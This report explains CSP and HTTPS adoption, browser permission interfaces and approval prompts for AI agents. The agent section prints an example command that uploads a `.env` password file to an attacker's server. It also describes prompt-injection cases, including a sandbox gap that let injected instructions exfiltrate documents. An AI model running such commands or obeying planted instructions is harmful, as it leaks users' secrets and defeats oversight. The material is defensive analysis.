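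By the end of the period, only 40 of the 10,000 sites had a script policy that the researchers considered meaningfully secure. One was GitHub, which gradually moved all its scripts to a single host of its own and never used `'unsafe-inline'`. Sixteen others were pornographic sites that listed identical sources and adopted CSP a week or two apart. Their operators had removed the inline event handlers from one site, found that the policy worked, and repeated the change on the rest.

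### Faults in the browsers

A well-written policy also depends on the browser enforcing it correctly. In *A Bug's Life*, Franken, Van Goethem and colleagues reproduced 75 CSP bugs in more than 100,000 historical versions of Chromium and Firefox. About half dated from when the browser first supported the standard version of CSP. The median bug went unreported for 2.9 years in Chromium and 1.2 years in Firefox. One severe flaw in Chromium weakened CSP for more than eight years.

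Script control is hard to implement because a page can load or create code in many ways. New windows, embedded frames and background workers all need their own checks, and each new browser feature may need its own check too. Twelve of the bugs came from attempts to fix other CSP bugs.

Browser makers didn't always share what they learned, even though they were implementing the same standard. Fourteen of the bugs appeared in both browsers, and the researchers judged that better communication between the two vendors could have prevented seven of them or led to earlier fixes.

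### Use in 2025 and 2026

CSP is now fairly common. The *Security* chapter of HTTP Archive's 2025 Web Almanac found it on 21.9% of sites, up from 18.5% a year earlier. Report URI's *10 years of watching the web* found policies on 170,057 of the 819,002 popular sites that responded in June 2026, compared with about 1,400 in 2016. Report URI sells CSP monitoring, so it has an interest in how people read these numbers, but its figure of 20.8% is close to HTTP Archive's.

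The studies disagree about `'unsafe-inline'` largely because they count different things:

| Source | Policies counted | With `'unsafe-inline'` | With nonces |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calzavara and colleagues | Sites enforcing any policy, March 2016 | 51.8% | 1.1% |
| Weichselbaum and colleagues | Distinct policies meant to control scripts, 2016 | 87.6% | About 1% |
| Roth and colleagues | Sites restricting scripts, 2018 | Almost 90% | 5% |
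| HTTP Archive | Policies with a script rule, 2025 | 92% | About 20% |
| Report URI | All policies, June 2026 | 46.8% | 24.7% |

Report URI's figure for `'unsafe-inline'` is low because many of the policies in its data have no script rule and so don't need the setting. HTTP Archive's 92% overstates the problem, because modern browsers ignore `'unsafe-inline'` when the policy also has a nonce, and careful sites include both so that their pages still work in older browsers. But even if every policy with a nonce also has `'unsafe-inline'`, around 70% of script policies have the unsafe setting and no nonce.

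The share of script policies that use nonces has grown from about 1% to about 20% in nine years. But on most sites that try to control scripts, the policy still does little to stop the attack in the hotel review.

### Why framing and HTTPS were easier

The most common CSP headers today don't list permitted script sources. About half of all policies contain `upgrade-insecure-requests`, and about half contain `frame-ancestors`.

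`frame-ancestors` controls which other sites may display a page inside a frame. It prevents clickjacking, in which an attacker lays an invisible copy of one page over a harmless one. For example, a visitor who tries to start a video might click a button on their bank's page instead. `upgrade-insecure-requests` makes the browser fetch everything on a page over HTTPS, even where an old link begins with http. Mozilla's original proposal had listed clickjacking and unencrypted content as secondary goals.

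Both settings take one short line, which can be the same on very different sites. A bank and a newspaper can both send `frame-ancestors 'none'` if nobody needs to embed their pages, without knowing which scripts those pages run or rewriting any code. But a script policy depends on everything in the page, including advertisements and analytics tools that other companies can change at any time.

The HTTPS setting also fixes insecure links, whereas a script rule would only block something. Roth and colleagues studied 251 sites that adopted the setting as they moved to HTTPS, and found that 77 still had old http links on their home pages within the first month. The browser corrected these links automatically, but it can't do this if the other server doesn't offer HTTPS. That was a likely reason why 28 of 46 sites later stopped enforcing HTTPS through CSP.

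Browser makers also had fewer chances to make mistakes with the framing and HTTPS rules, because the checks for them sit in only a few places in the browser's code. Of the 75 bugs that Franken and colleagues studied, 61 let a page get around content restrictions, while two concerned framing and one concerned HTTPS.

CSP's reputation discouraged sites from using even its easy parts. In December 2018, 3,253 of the sites in Roth's study still used an older and less consistent header against clickjacking, while 409 used CSP's `frame-ancestors` directive. The researchers emailed 2,699 sites to explain the newer option. Many of those who replied hadn't known they could use it without writing a script policy, and 24 said CSP was too complex for them. Within eight days, the number of sites using `frame-ancestors` rose from 511 to 554.

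### Who writes the policy

To write a safe script policy, a site owner has to know every script the site needs and whether any permitted host could serve an attacker's code. The owner also has to keep this information up to date, though most of the relevant changes happen outside the site. If the policy blocks a script the site needs, the site breaks at once, perhaps on the payment page, but a policy that allows too much has no visible effect until someone attacks. These difficulties probably help explain why so many owners chose `'unsafe-inline'`.

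Allow-lists for agents take similar work to write and can fail in the same way, as the bug-fixing assistant's list of shell commands did in IBM's tests. If every website or company has to write its own rules for agents, many will probably write rules that look strict but permit nearly everything.

Google's changes to its own policies are a good counter-example to this pessimism. Google Maps Activities, an application with 4 million monthly users, adopted an allow-list in February 2015. Its developers made five major changes that year, and the list still included a host with a JSONP weakness. They then switched to nonces and `'strict-dynamic'`. The switch needed no rewriting because the application already put nonces on its scripts, and the developers had not had to change the policy again by the time they published their paper. Google also used the approach for Google Photos and several other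 products.

A page's templates can add the nonce to every approved script automatically, so nobody has to maintain a list of hosts. Report URI lists Dropbox, Meta, X, Reddit and Discord among the sites whose policies use nonces.

Some evidence suggests that Google's users became safer. According to Report URI's *Client-Side Security Reporting*, cross-site scripting fell from 30% of the rewards Google paid for vulnerability reports in 2018 to 4.1% in 2023. Report URI attributes this drop to the move to CSP, but the share would also have fallen if Google had made its code safer in other ways or paid more for other kinds of bugs.

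Roth and colleagues found that google.com also changed its policy, dropping `'strict-dynamic'` in July 2018. Google's engineers had come to prefer having each trusted script pass the nonce on explicitly, partly because Safari didn't support the keyword. A hotel with a booking page probably can't keep up with such changes as well as a company with its own browser and security team can.

Smaller sites can get a policy from the platform that hosts them. HTTP Archive found CSP on about 96% of sites made with GoDaddy's website builder and on nearly every LiveJournal page, although it didn't report how strict those policies were. A platform's default policy doesn't necessarily block attacks. In March 2016, Calzavara and colleagues found that 3,432 online shops, 42% of the sites they found using CSP, sent the same policy because Shopify supplied it. That policy was in report-only mode, so it blocked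 nothing, and many shop owners may not have known it was there.

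## How did HTTPS go from an option to the default?

HTTPS is the encrypted version of HTTP, the protocol that carries web pages between sites and browsers. For about twenty years after its invention in 1994, most sites did not use it. Since the autumn of 2026, Chrome has asked for the user's permission before opening a public site without HTTPS. HTTPS works in much the same way on very different sites, as CSP's framing rule does.

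### What HTTPS protects

Felt, Barnes and colleagues explain in *Measuring HTTPS Adoption on the Web* (2017) that HTTPS prevents anyone between the browser and the server from reading what they exchange or changing it unnoticed, and that it uses a certificate to show that the server belongs to the site in the address bar. A certificate authority, an organisation that browsers trust to issue certificates, checks that the applicant controls the site's name before issuing one.

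When an employee opens a travel site over HTTP on hotel Wi-Fi, anyone who controls the network can read the passport number the employee types or rewrite the page. If an agent is reading the page, the attacker can also inject a prompt by adding an instruction in transit, without posting a review or breaking into the site.

HTTPS does not protect against a hostile review already on the site, because the server encrypts and delivers it with the rest of the page. CSP addresses that attack, but it needs HTTPS because someone who can rewrite a page in transit can also remove its policy.

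An attacker needs only one unencrypted page load to redirect a browser. Thompson, Acer and colleagues (2025) point out in *HTTPS by default*, Google's announcement of the Chrome change, that many HTTP addresses only redirect the browser to an HTTPS site. If the employee follows an old link to `http://travel.example`, an attacker on the network can answer before the real site does and send the browser somewhere else, perhaps to a page that installs malware. Normally the redirect takes a moment and the address bar then shows HTTPS, so the employee cannot tell that the first step was exposed.

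### An option for payments and passwords

Netscape, which made the leading browser of the mid-1990s, introduced HTTPS mainly to protect payments and passwords. The IETF described it in an RFC in May 2000. Many sites encrypted only the login page and sent everything after login over HTTP.

In October 2010 the developer Eric Butler released Firesheep, a Firefox extension that let people with no technical skill exploit an old weakness. After a login, a site recognises the visitor by a cookie, and many sites sent this cookie unencrypted. Firesheep intercepted these cookies on open Wi-Fi, listed the people nearby who were logged in to sites such as Facebook, and let its user enter their accounts with a double click. Gmail had already made HTTPS its default that January, and Twitter did so in early 2012.

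The IETF published HTTP Strict Transport Security (HSTS) in November 2012. It lets a site commit itself to HTTPS with a header:

```
Strict-Transport-Security: max-age=31536000; includeSubDomains
```

After a site sends the HTTP Strict Transport Security (HSTS) header over HTTPS with a lifetime of one year (31,536,000 seconds), the browser changes every http link to that site into an https one before it connects. *The State of https Adoption on the Web* (Kerschbaumer, Braun and colleagues, 2025), a study by Mozilla staff, explains that the browser ignores the header if it arrives over HTTP, so a first visit can still be unprotected. Browser makers closed this gap for some sites by shipping browsers with a preload list, which had about 106,000 entries in early 2025.

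Many sites use HSTS only partially. Helme (2026), in *Top 1 Million Analysis*, found the HSTS header on about 31% of popular sites in June 2026, but only 21% of those sites had the settings that the preload list requires. Scott Helme runs Report URI, and the figures come from the same crawl as its CSP data.

### Free certificates

Every HTTPS site needs a certificate, and until late 2015 most owners had to buy one. *Let's Encrypt* (Aas, Barnes and colleagues, 2019) gives an average price of $178 a year for one domain from the five largest certificate authorities, and $766 for a certificate that also covered subdomains. Owners also had to generate a key, prove control of the domain, install the files and repeat the work when the certificate expired. Usability studies found that installation alone often took administrators over an hour. About 20% of trusted certificates expired before anyone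 renewed them.

Let's Encrypt is a certificate authority that issues certificates automatically and for free. A group at the University of Michigan and the Electronic Frontier Foundation (EFF), a digital rights organisation, began designing the process in 2012, while a team at Mozilla was planning a separate free authority. The two groups began working together in May 2013 and opened the service to the public in December 2015.

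A program on the website's server does the owner's work:

1. It asks Let's Encrypt for a certificate for, say, `travel.example`.
2. Let's Encrypt sends back a challenge, usually to publish a particular value at an address on that site.
3. The program publishes the value, and Let's Encrypt fetches it to confirm that the applicant controls the domain.
4. Let's Encrypt issues the certificate, and the program installs it.
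5. The program repeats the process before the certificate expires, after 90 days.

The founders chose the short certificate lifetime partly to push owners towards automation, since few people would want to renew certificates by hand every quarter. They also argue that free certificates and automation depend on each other. An authority that gives away millions of certificates can't pay people to check each one.

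By January 2019, Let's Encrypt had issued 538 million certificates for 223 million domain names. Part of this growth came from hosting companies and publishing platforms that obtained certificates for all their customers, many of whom probably never thought about encryption. The largest of these providers accounted for about a third of the names.

### Pressure from browsers

Browser makers also began to reserve new features for secure pages. W3C's Secure Contexts specification sets out the rule, and browsers enforce it. In April 2016, Chrome stopped giving HTTP pages the user's location. Service workers, scripts that let a site work offline, have the same restriction. A travel site that wanted to show nearby hotels now had a reason to switch to HTTPS, even if its owner wasn't very concerned about eavesdropping.

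Next, in early 2017, Firefox and Chrome started warning people about HTTP pages that asked for passwords or card numbers. In July 2018, Chrome began labelling every HTTP page "Not secure". Browsers had previously marked HTTPS pages as safe, and Aas and colleagues thought users might mistake that mark for approval of a site's content. Marking HTTP pages instead made sense only once they had become less common.

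Google and the White House also pushed sites towards HTTPS. In August 2014 Google began ranking HTTPS sites slightly higher in its search results, and in 2015 the White House told federal agencies to use HTTPS on all their public sites.

### How far HTTPS spread

| Measure | Earlier | Later |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome page loads over HTTPS (Google) | 30–45% in 2015 | 95–99% around 2020, then a plateau |
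| Firefox page loads over HTTPS (Kerschbaumer and colleagues) | Under 30% in 2014 | Over 80% at the end of 2024 |
| 100 top sites that redirect to HTTPS (Felt and colleagues) | 24% in February 2016 | 44% in February 2017 |
| Top million sites that redirect to HTTPS (Felt and colleagues) | 5% in April 2016 | 10% in February 2017 |
| Top million sites that redirect to HTTPS (Helme) | Under 7% in August 2015 | 80% in June 2026 |

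The share of page loads using HTTPS rose well before the share of sites using it. EFF (2017) reported that about half of web traffic used HTTPS that February, when only a tenth of the top million sites redirected visitors to it. Thompson, Savage and colleagues (2018) explain that a minority of popular sites accounted for most of the protected pages.

The share of page loads that use HTTPS also depends on how people browse. Felt and colleagues imagine two people who run the same Google search and read the same nine HTTP results. One opens each result in a new tab, so 1 page load in 10 uses HTTPS. The other presses "Back" after each result, which reloads Google's encrypted page, so about half of the page loads use HTTPS.

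The gap between Chrome and Firefox is also partly due to differences in counting. Mozilla's older measurements understate HTTPS use, and its researchers added new ones for January and February 2025. In the new data, about 92% of Firefox page loads used HTTPS, 5.5% went to HTTP addresses on local networks, and 2.4% went to other HTTP sites. Excluding the local addresses, the HTTPS share is about 97%.

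### What still uses HTTP

Local addresses are the largest part of the remainder in Google's data too. A home router often has a settings page at `192.168.0.1`, and a company may have an internal site called `intranet/`. A certificate authority checks that an applicant controls an address, but millions of routers share `192.168.0.1` and nobody owns it. The rules for publicly trusted certificates therefore don't allow one for such an address. The owner of a router or internal site can make their own certificate, but browsers will warn about it unless each user installs it by hand.

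This explains why Linux users seem to be so far behind. Only 84% of their page loads in Chrome use HTTPS, but nearly 97% do when only public sites are counted. On Windows, the figure rises from 95% to 98%. Kerschbaumer and colleagues suggest that a larger share of Linux users are developers and system administrators, who spend a lot of time on local machines.

Some public sites also stayed on HTTP because they had to contact local devices. For example, a manufacturer's set-up page might send commands to a new printer. The printer had no certificate, and browsers blocked HTTPS pages from contacting it, so the manufacturer had to leave the page unencrypted. Chrome now lets an HTTPS page reach local devices if the user gives permission.

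Other HTTP traffic comes from redirects that companies never updated. HTTPS use also varies by country. In Firefox's 2025 data, HTTPS carried over 95% of page loads in North America and Europe, but an average of 72% in ten of the world's least developed countries and only 51% in Sudan. Low figures can rise quickly. Japan was far behind in 2017, when the median Firefox user there loaded 37% of pages over HTTPS, but by 2025 the country's overall figure was about 94%.

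### Asking before the connection

Chrome's developers concluded that labels would not eliminate the remaining insecure HTTP connections. DeBlasio, Trouton and colleagues (2026) give three reasons in *Chrome Now Warns Before Insecure HTTP Connections*. People often overlook labels. A redirect finishes before the browser can show one. Most importantly, a label appears only after the connection has exposed the user's data.

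A browser can instead try HTTPS first, even if the link uses HTTP. Firefox has done this for all page loads since version 136 in early 2025, and it falls back to HTTP without asking if the secure connection fails. Mozilla's *Firefox Security Privacy Newsletter 2025 Q1* (2025) reports that HTTPS requests rose by at least 1.5%. The fallback keeps old sites working, but an attacker can presumably trigger it by blocking the secure connection.

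With Chrome's "Always Use Secure Connections" setting on, the browser warns the user when HTTPS fails and waits for permission before trying HTTP. Google introduced the setting in 2022 as an opt-in. Few people turn on settings of this kind. About 2 million Firefox users have ever enabled that browser's equivalent, compared with over 140 million users who contributed to Mozilla's 2025 data, and a third of those who enabled it later switched it off.

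Google had to make the warnings rare before it could make the setting a default. In 2024 it added a version that covers only public sites, so people who work with routers and intranets don't see warnings there. Chrome also remembers a user's permission for 15 days and renews it at each visit, so someone who regularly reads an HTTP site may see the warning only once.

Google then turned on the public-sites version for a small percentage of users in Chrome 141. The median user saw fewer than one warning a week, and the user at the 95th percentile saw fewer than three. A coding agent that asks for approval before every command can show more prompts than that in a few minutes.

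Google announced its plan in October 2025, a year ahead, and contacted the organisations responsible for the most HTTP page loads. It scheduled the change for Chrome 147 in April 2026 for the more than 1 billion people who had chosen Chrome's Enhanced Safe Browsing protection. Everyone else would get it in Chrome 154. 窓の杜's *「Google Chrome 154」が公開* (2026), a Japanese news report, dates that version's first desktop release to 22 September. On 21 October, Google announced that the HTTPS protection was now on by default for all users.

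Early figures from the full rollout are a little better than the experiment's. *Chrome puts insecure sites behind a permission prompt* (Pogorelec, 2026) quotes Google as saying that nearly 95% of desktop users see no warning in a given week and under 1% see three or more. Google says Chrome is the first browser to turn this protection on for everyone. Safari, Firefox and Edge also try HTTPS first, but their warnings are still optional.

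### What caused the rise?

Standards alone did not make HTTPS the default. In 2015, 15 years after HTTPS became an IETF specification, at least 55% of page loads in Chrome still used HTTP. Some later advances came before their standards. Let's Encrypt had been issuing certificates to the public for over three years when its protocol became an IETF RFC in 2019. In early 2025, browser makers were still discussing a common rule for automatic upgrades to HTTPS, though several had already shipped their own.

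The falling price of certificates explains the move to HTTPS better for small sites than for large ones. A $178 certificate would hardly have deterred the world's hundred most popular sites, yet the share of them that redirected to HTTPS nearly doubled in the year to February 2017. Felt and colleagues attribute this increase to public demand and to features that worked only on secure pages. They credit Let's Encrypt and publishing platforms such as Squarespace for adoption among smaller sites.

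Later adoption figures support the second part of that account. The same researchers predicted that smaller sites would need another five years unless a tool or hosting service produced a breakthrough. By March 2020, three years later, Helme counted 528,498 of the top million sites redirecting to HTTPS. The two crawls used different lists and tests, but those differences can't explain a rise from about 10% to more than half. Automated certificates probably provided the breakthrough the researchers had described.

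Let's Encrypt's founders go further and credit it with significant growth in HTTPS. They are hardly neutral, although Aas (2025), in *A Note from our Executive Director*, concedes that the project "can't claim all the credit". A free certificate doesn't secure a site unless the site uses it. *Shedding Light on the Adoption of Let's Encrypt* (2016), an early Carnegie Mellon University study, found that only 54% of domains were using the certificates they had obtained.

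The effect of browser pressure is harder to isolate, because the feature restrictions and the labels arrived in the same years as free certificates. Kerschbaumer and colleagues list all these causes without trying to separate them. Chrome has labeled every HTTP page since 2018, but progress still largely stopped around 2020, which suggests that labels weren't enough to finish the move. Google found that many of the remaining companies could switch without much difficulty but hadn't paid attention. A deadline after which their visitors would see a warning gave them a reason to pay attention.

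Mandates also worked where someone had the authority to issue them, though no one has that authority over the whole web. 18F, a federal technology office, reported in *Tracking the US government's progress on moving to HTTPS* (2017) that HTTPS went from a clear minority to a clear majority of executive-branch sites after the White House policy, and that adoption on those sites overtook adoption in the private sector.

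Surveillance revelations are the hardest cause to test. Edward Snowden began disclosing the US government's mass surveillance in June 2013. Felt and colleagues say industry-wide efforts followed public attention to surveillance and tampering, and they cite later cases such as internet providers inserting advertisements into pages. But Gmail had switched three years before Snowden's disclosures, and the founders of Let's Encrypt had started working together the month before. The browser data in these studies starts in 2014 at the earliest, so it can't show whether growth sped up after the disclosures. The disclosures may well have made managers more willing to approve work that engineers already wanted to do.

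### The burden on small sites

Chrome's warning pressures site owners who may have little money or expertise. Mayer, Krombholz and colleagues found in *Securing the Internet, One HTTP 200 OK at a Time* that setting up HTTPS securely can be challenging even for experienced administrators. A village club with a website built by a volunteer in 2009 may have nobody who knows how to do it.

Adopting HTTPS is much less of a burden for site owners than it would have been in 2015. Chromium's *Adapting your website for Chrome's "Ask-before-HTTP" warning*, a guide from the open-source project behind Chrome, notes that common web servers can now obtain certificates automatically and that modern hosting companies support HTTPS. In many cases the owner only has to switch it on.

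Some problems are outside a site owner's control. A site can use HTTPS on every page and still cause a warning because a domain-forwarding company sends visitors to it through an HTTP address. The owner then has to persuade that company to change, or switch to another.

Chrome also shows the warnings mainly to new visitors, since it remembers the regular ones. A small shop may depend on new visitors, and some of them will presumably turn back. Google's figures show how many warnings each user sees but not how many visitors each site loses, so they can't settle this objection.

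Kerschbaumer and colleagues argue against having browsers refuse HTTP altogether, because that would block access to valuable old sites that nobody maintains. They suggest blocking only HTTP sites created after a fixed date, which would keep the 2009 club page accessible but require a newly built shop to use encryption. Browsers don't yet have a reliable way to tell how old a site is. Chrome's prompt lets visitors continue to either site with one extra click.

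## How did permission prompts become shared browser interfaces, and do people decide well with them?

Chrome's warning about HTTP sites is a permission prompt, like those that ask whether a site may use the visitor's location or camera, or send notifications. Browsers now handle these permissions through shared interfaces, though each browser still words its own prompts. Studies have found that phone users and people supervising agents often approve requests they haven't read or don't understand.

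### From separate prompts to shared interfaces

Browser makers added features such as location and notifications one at a time, and each feature handled permission differently. *Permissions API*, a page of Mozilla's developer documentation, notes that sites could check whether they had permission to send notifications but not whether they had permission to use location. A travel site that wanted to show nearby hotels had to request the user's location to find out whether it had permission, which could trigger a prompt as soon as someone opened the page.

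The Permissions API gives sites one way to check the state of any permission it covers:

```
navigator.permissions.query({ name: "geolocation" })
```

The result is `granted`, `denied` or `prompt`, where `prompt` means the browser will ask the user. If the result is `prompt`, the travel site can wait to request the location until the user presses a "Hotels near me" button, so the reason for the request is obvious. If it is `denied`, the site can offer a box for typing a city name. The site can also ask the browser to notify it when the user changes the setting.

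Permissions Policy controls which parts of a page may use a feature at all. Suppose the travel site's page contains a map from one company and an advertisement from another. The site can send this header:

```
Permissions-Policy: geolocation=(self "https://maps.example"), camera=()
```

If the site also adds `allow="geolocation"` to the map's frame, the map can request the visitor's location but the advertisement can't. The visitor can still refuse the map's request. No code on the page can use the camera, including the site's own. When the policy blocks a feature, the Permissions API reports `denied` and the browser shows no prompt.

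The first public draft of this second interface, W3C's *Feature Policy* (2019), is dated 16 April 2019. In May 2020, Google engineer Clelland (2020) told W3C's working group that there was rough consensus to rename it Permissions Policy. The new name required a new header, and that September Clelland announced that Google planned to replace the old header with it in Chrome. Sites that had adopted the old header had to write another, as early users of CSP had.

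Many site owners will never write either header, so visitors' protection depends more on the browser's default than on the syntax. In a planning entry, *[meta] Feature Policy allow attribute MVP*, Mozilla planned to deny embedded third-party pages access to the camera, microphone and location unless the outer page allowed it.

Neither interface is a finished standard. The June 2026 versions of the Permissions API and W3C's *Permissions Policy* (2026) are both Working Drafts. The specifications for the features they govern also vary in status. W3C's *Permissions Registry* cites, for example, a 2022 Recommendation for location and a WHATWG Living Standard for notifications, but only a Community Group draft for access to the fonts on a person's computer.

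The specifications also leave the prompt to browser makers, who decide what to ask, which buttons to offer and how long to remember the answer. Browser makers could therefore improve their prompts without waiting for W3C to agree on new text.

### Did Android users read the list?

Some of the best early evidence on permission prompts comes from phones. In 2011, Android showed people a list of permissions when they installed an app. They could accept the whole list or cancel the installation, and they never saw the list again during normal use.

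Felt, Ha and colleagues (2012), in *Android Permissions*, surveyed 308 Android users online and watched others install apps in a coffee shop. The researchers hid their interest in security and asked the people in the coffee shop to find a coupon app on their own phones. Of the 24 people whose attention they could assess, 4 looked at the list of permissions, 10 knew about it but skipped it, and 10 didn't know it existed.

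People who read the list of permissions didn't always understand it. Only 8 of 302 survey respondents correctly answered all three questions about what permissions allowed. The permission to make phone calls appeared under the large heading "Services that cost you money", and almost as many people thought it let an app charge their credit card as knew it let the app place calls.

Three of the people who skipped the list said they used to read it. About 90% of apps showed permission warnings, so a careful user would have seen one nearly every time and would usually have had no reason to cancel.

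The prompts still helped some people. A fifth of the interview participants could describe canceling an installation because of its permissions. About a quarter had learned about permissions from reviews, which suggests that a few attentive users can warn others. But an agent's approval prompt usually concerns one person's files at one moment, so nobody else is likely to have reviewed the same action.

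### Asking at the moment of use

Android 6.0 began asking for permission to use sensitive data when an app first tries to use it, instead of at installation. iPhones already worked this way. Users can now see what the app is doing when it asks, and can refuse one permission without giving up the app.

Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues (2015), in *Android Permissions Remystified*, tested how well this approach might work. They gave 36 people modified phones to use for a week and recorded each time an app used a permission. They then showed participants screenshots of what they had been doing when an app requested sensitive data. Participants would have blocked 35% of the 423 requests they were shown, most often because the app didn't seem to need the data. Six people would have allowed every request.

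Asking people every time would have been impossible, because apps made about 213 requests an hour for each person, even counting only those that exposed data such as a location or text message. But asking only once is also a problem, because later requests may be much less reasonable than the first. Someone might let a map app see their location while looking for a restaurant, without expecting it to keep checking overnight. Three-quarters of all permission requests came when the person had no visible sign that the app was running.

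Wijesekera and colleagues proposed software that predicts which requests would surprise a person and asks only about those. Anthropic's auto mode applies a similar idea to agents.

Browser makers have tried simpler fixes. Chrome users ignored, dismissed or refused most notification prompts, so in 2020 Google introduced a quieter prompt that doesn't interrupt the page. Chrome uses it for people who usually refuse and for sites whose requests few people accept. Android and Chrome also withdraw permissions from apps and sites that a person has stopped using, which limits the harm from an old approval.

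Another fix is to tie the permission request to something the person is already doing. Felt and colleagues describe an early version by Franziska Roesner and others, in which users granted permission through ordinary actions. Chrome's `<geolocation>` element works similarly. The browser draws a location button inside the page and starts the request when the visitor clicks it.

Chrome's permission for reaching local devices helped printer set-up pages move to HTTPS, and it also added a new prompt. Before, sites could often contact a visitor's router or printer without the visitor knowing. Few people would expect a news site to do that, so they are more likely to learn something useful from this prompt than from another request to send notifications.

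### How often people approve an agent's actions

Within weeks of Claude Code's launch, users showed approval fatigue, paying less attention as prompts accumulated, according to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported in March 2026 that users approved 93% of permission prompts, and by August the company's figure was 97%.

Many people stop reviewing commands. Anthropic reported that by June 2026, 62% of Claude Code users had at some point turned off permission checks or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions began with the checks off. People seem to do this more as they gain experience. Resilient Cyber's *the human in the loop illusion*, which summarises another Anthropic study, reports that new users approved everything automatically in about 20% of sessions, while people with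 750 sessions did so in over 40%.

Permission prompts differ between products, even those from the same company. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) examined five agents from Anthropic and OpenAI in May and June 2026. ChatGPT's chat mode required approval for every action covered by a permission setting, and they found no way to approve actions in advance. In ChatGPT's agent mode, which controls a remote browser, they couldn't set any permissions for the browser. They conclude that commercial agents often make users choose between frequent prompts and an automatic reviewer that users can't inspect or control.

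A high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. If 97 of every 100 commands are harmless, a perfect reviewer will approve 97%. Anthropic also found that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents, compared with 3% of individual actions. This suggests people pay more attention to plans, though they may reject a plan because they dislike the approach rather than because they think it is dangerous.

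### One bad command among sixty

Suppose a developer asks an agent to fix a fault in the travel site's booking code. The agent asks for approval 60 times during the afternoon, and these are five of the commands:

```
52  pytest tests/booking
53  git diff
54  curl -F file=@.env https://test-logs.example/upload
55  pytest tests/booking
56  git diff
```

Most of the commands run tests or display changes to the code. The 54th sends the `.env` file, which contains the site's passwords, to a server an attacker controls. An instruction planted in a file the agent read earlier described this as uploading the test logs. The command is one line long, like the ones around it, and the developer has correctly approved the previous 53.

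A developer who approves all 60 prompts will be right 59 times, or about 98% of the time, but will still lose the passwords. Reading the first 53 carefully brings no benefit, because approving them unread has the same result.

Anthropic tested whether people notice dangerous commands in approval prompts, using 1,053 paid testers working on coding tasks. Partway through each session, the company replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. Testers caught about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands and did no worse in long sessions.

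The test favours the classifier in some ways. The testers worked in someone else's test environment, so mistakes had no consequences for them, and Anthropic has a product to promote. But the testers also knew they were being evaluated, which should have made them more careful, and the fall from 17% to 5% is hard to explain without some kind of fatigue.

Anthropic also looked at real sessions that its safety systems had flagged for review. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own mode, so differences in their work could explain some of the gap.

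### Why other studies found better decisions

Two other experiments found that people stopped many more bad actions. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day of email and travel. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026), volunteers judged actions in office tasks, and the experiment compared several kinds of prompt.

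| Study and prompt | People | Bad actions among those shown | Bad actions stopped |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic, ordinary command prompt | 1,053 | One per coding session | 13.6% |
| Yan, plain-language prompt for every action | 34 | 7 of 18 | 59.6% |
| Hossain and colleagues, short description | 20 | 6 of 12 | 45.0% |
| Hossain and colleagues, consequence explained | 20 | 6 of 12 | 75.8% |

The studies used different tasks and prompts, so the table can't show exactly why their results differ. One likely reason is that bad actions were much more common in the two smaller experiments, and a person who has just refused two requests will probably read the next one. Real agents misbehave much less often than every second or third action, so people using them may behave more like Anthropic's testers.

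"Bad" also means different things in these studies. Yan counted any action beyond the assigned task as bad, including a call to the airport to confirm a flight. Of the people who had to approve every action, 88% allowed that call, and some of them may have thought it was a good idea. Only 35% of the same group let the agent read recent bank transactions.

### What the prompt leaves out

A person can pay close attention and still not have enough information to decide. Hossain and colleagues give the example of a user who tells an agent to send an auditor only the totals from a set of invoices. A planted instruction makes the agent put every row of the invoices in a file called `report.csv`. The agent then requests approval to email the file. The recipient is correct and the filename looks ordinary, so nothing in the request reveals that the file contains more than the totals.

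The experiment added information in steps. With a short description of the action, people approved 55.0% of unsafe requests. Showing its exact details reduced this to 43.3%, and adding the user's original instructions and a log of earlier steps reduced it to 32.5%. The last version contained the same facts as the log but put the consequence in one statement, such as that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows. People approved 24.2% with this version, although the difference from the log version could be due to chance.

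Better information slowed decisions, from a median of 16 seconds with the short description to 33 seconds with the consequence statement. At 33 seconds each, the developer's 60 prompts would take about half an hour of the afternoon. People were also slightly more likely to refuse legitimate requests when they saw the consequence statement.

Most approval prompts in use show only a raw command on a single line, according to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026). *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026), a study of 290 reports of agents damaging files, gives the example of `python3 setup.py`, from which even a programmer can't tell what the script will do. User review played a part in 105 of the reports. Automatic approval was a factor in 80 and uninformative prompts in 31, with some overlap.

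A browser can use one location prompt for every website because "use your location" means roughly the same thing on each. An agent's request to "send a file" is harder to standardize because it may be harmless or disastrous, depending on what the file contains and what the user asked for earlier. Better wording can't entirely fix this, so a shared interface for agent permissions would have to include some of that context. Otherwise, its prompts would be consistent but not much more useful.

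### Replacing prompts with boundaries

An agent in a sandbox doesn't need to ask permission for actions that stay inside it. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes a sandbox for Claude Code that limits which folders the agent can change and which servers it can contact. The agent can run tests within these limits without asking, but it must ask the user before contacting a new server. Anthropic reports that the sandbox cut permission prompts by 84%.

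An 84% cut would leave the developer with about 10 prompts instead of 60. The upload of the password file would still trigger one, because it uses a new server. If the developer behaved like Anthropic's testers early in their sessions, the chance of catching the upload would rise from about 5% to 17%, but about five out of six people would still approve it. A sandbox that refused unknown servers would stop the upload every time, but it would also block some legitimate work.

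Anthropic chose firmer limits for Claude Cowork, its agent for general office work, because it didn't expect the typical user to understand shell commands. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, a separate simulated computer that can reach only the folders the user has shared, so the user doesn't have to judge each command.

This boundary had a gap much like the one in CSP's allow-lists. Cowork needed access to Anthropic's servers, so their address was on the sandbox's approved list. Instructions in a malicious file could therefore make the agent upload the user's documents to an attacker's Anthropic account, and the sandbox would allow it. Anthropic fixed this by accepting only requests that carried the session's own credentials.

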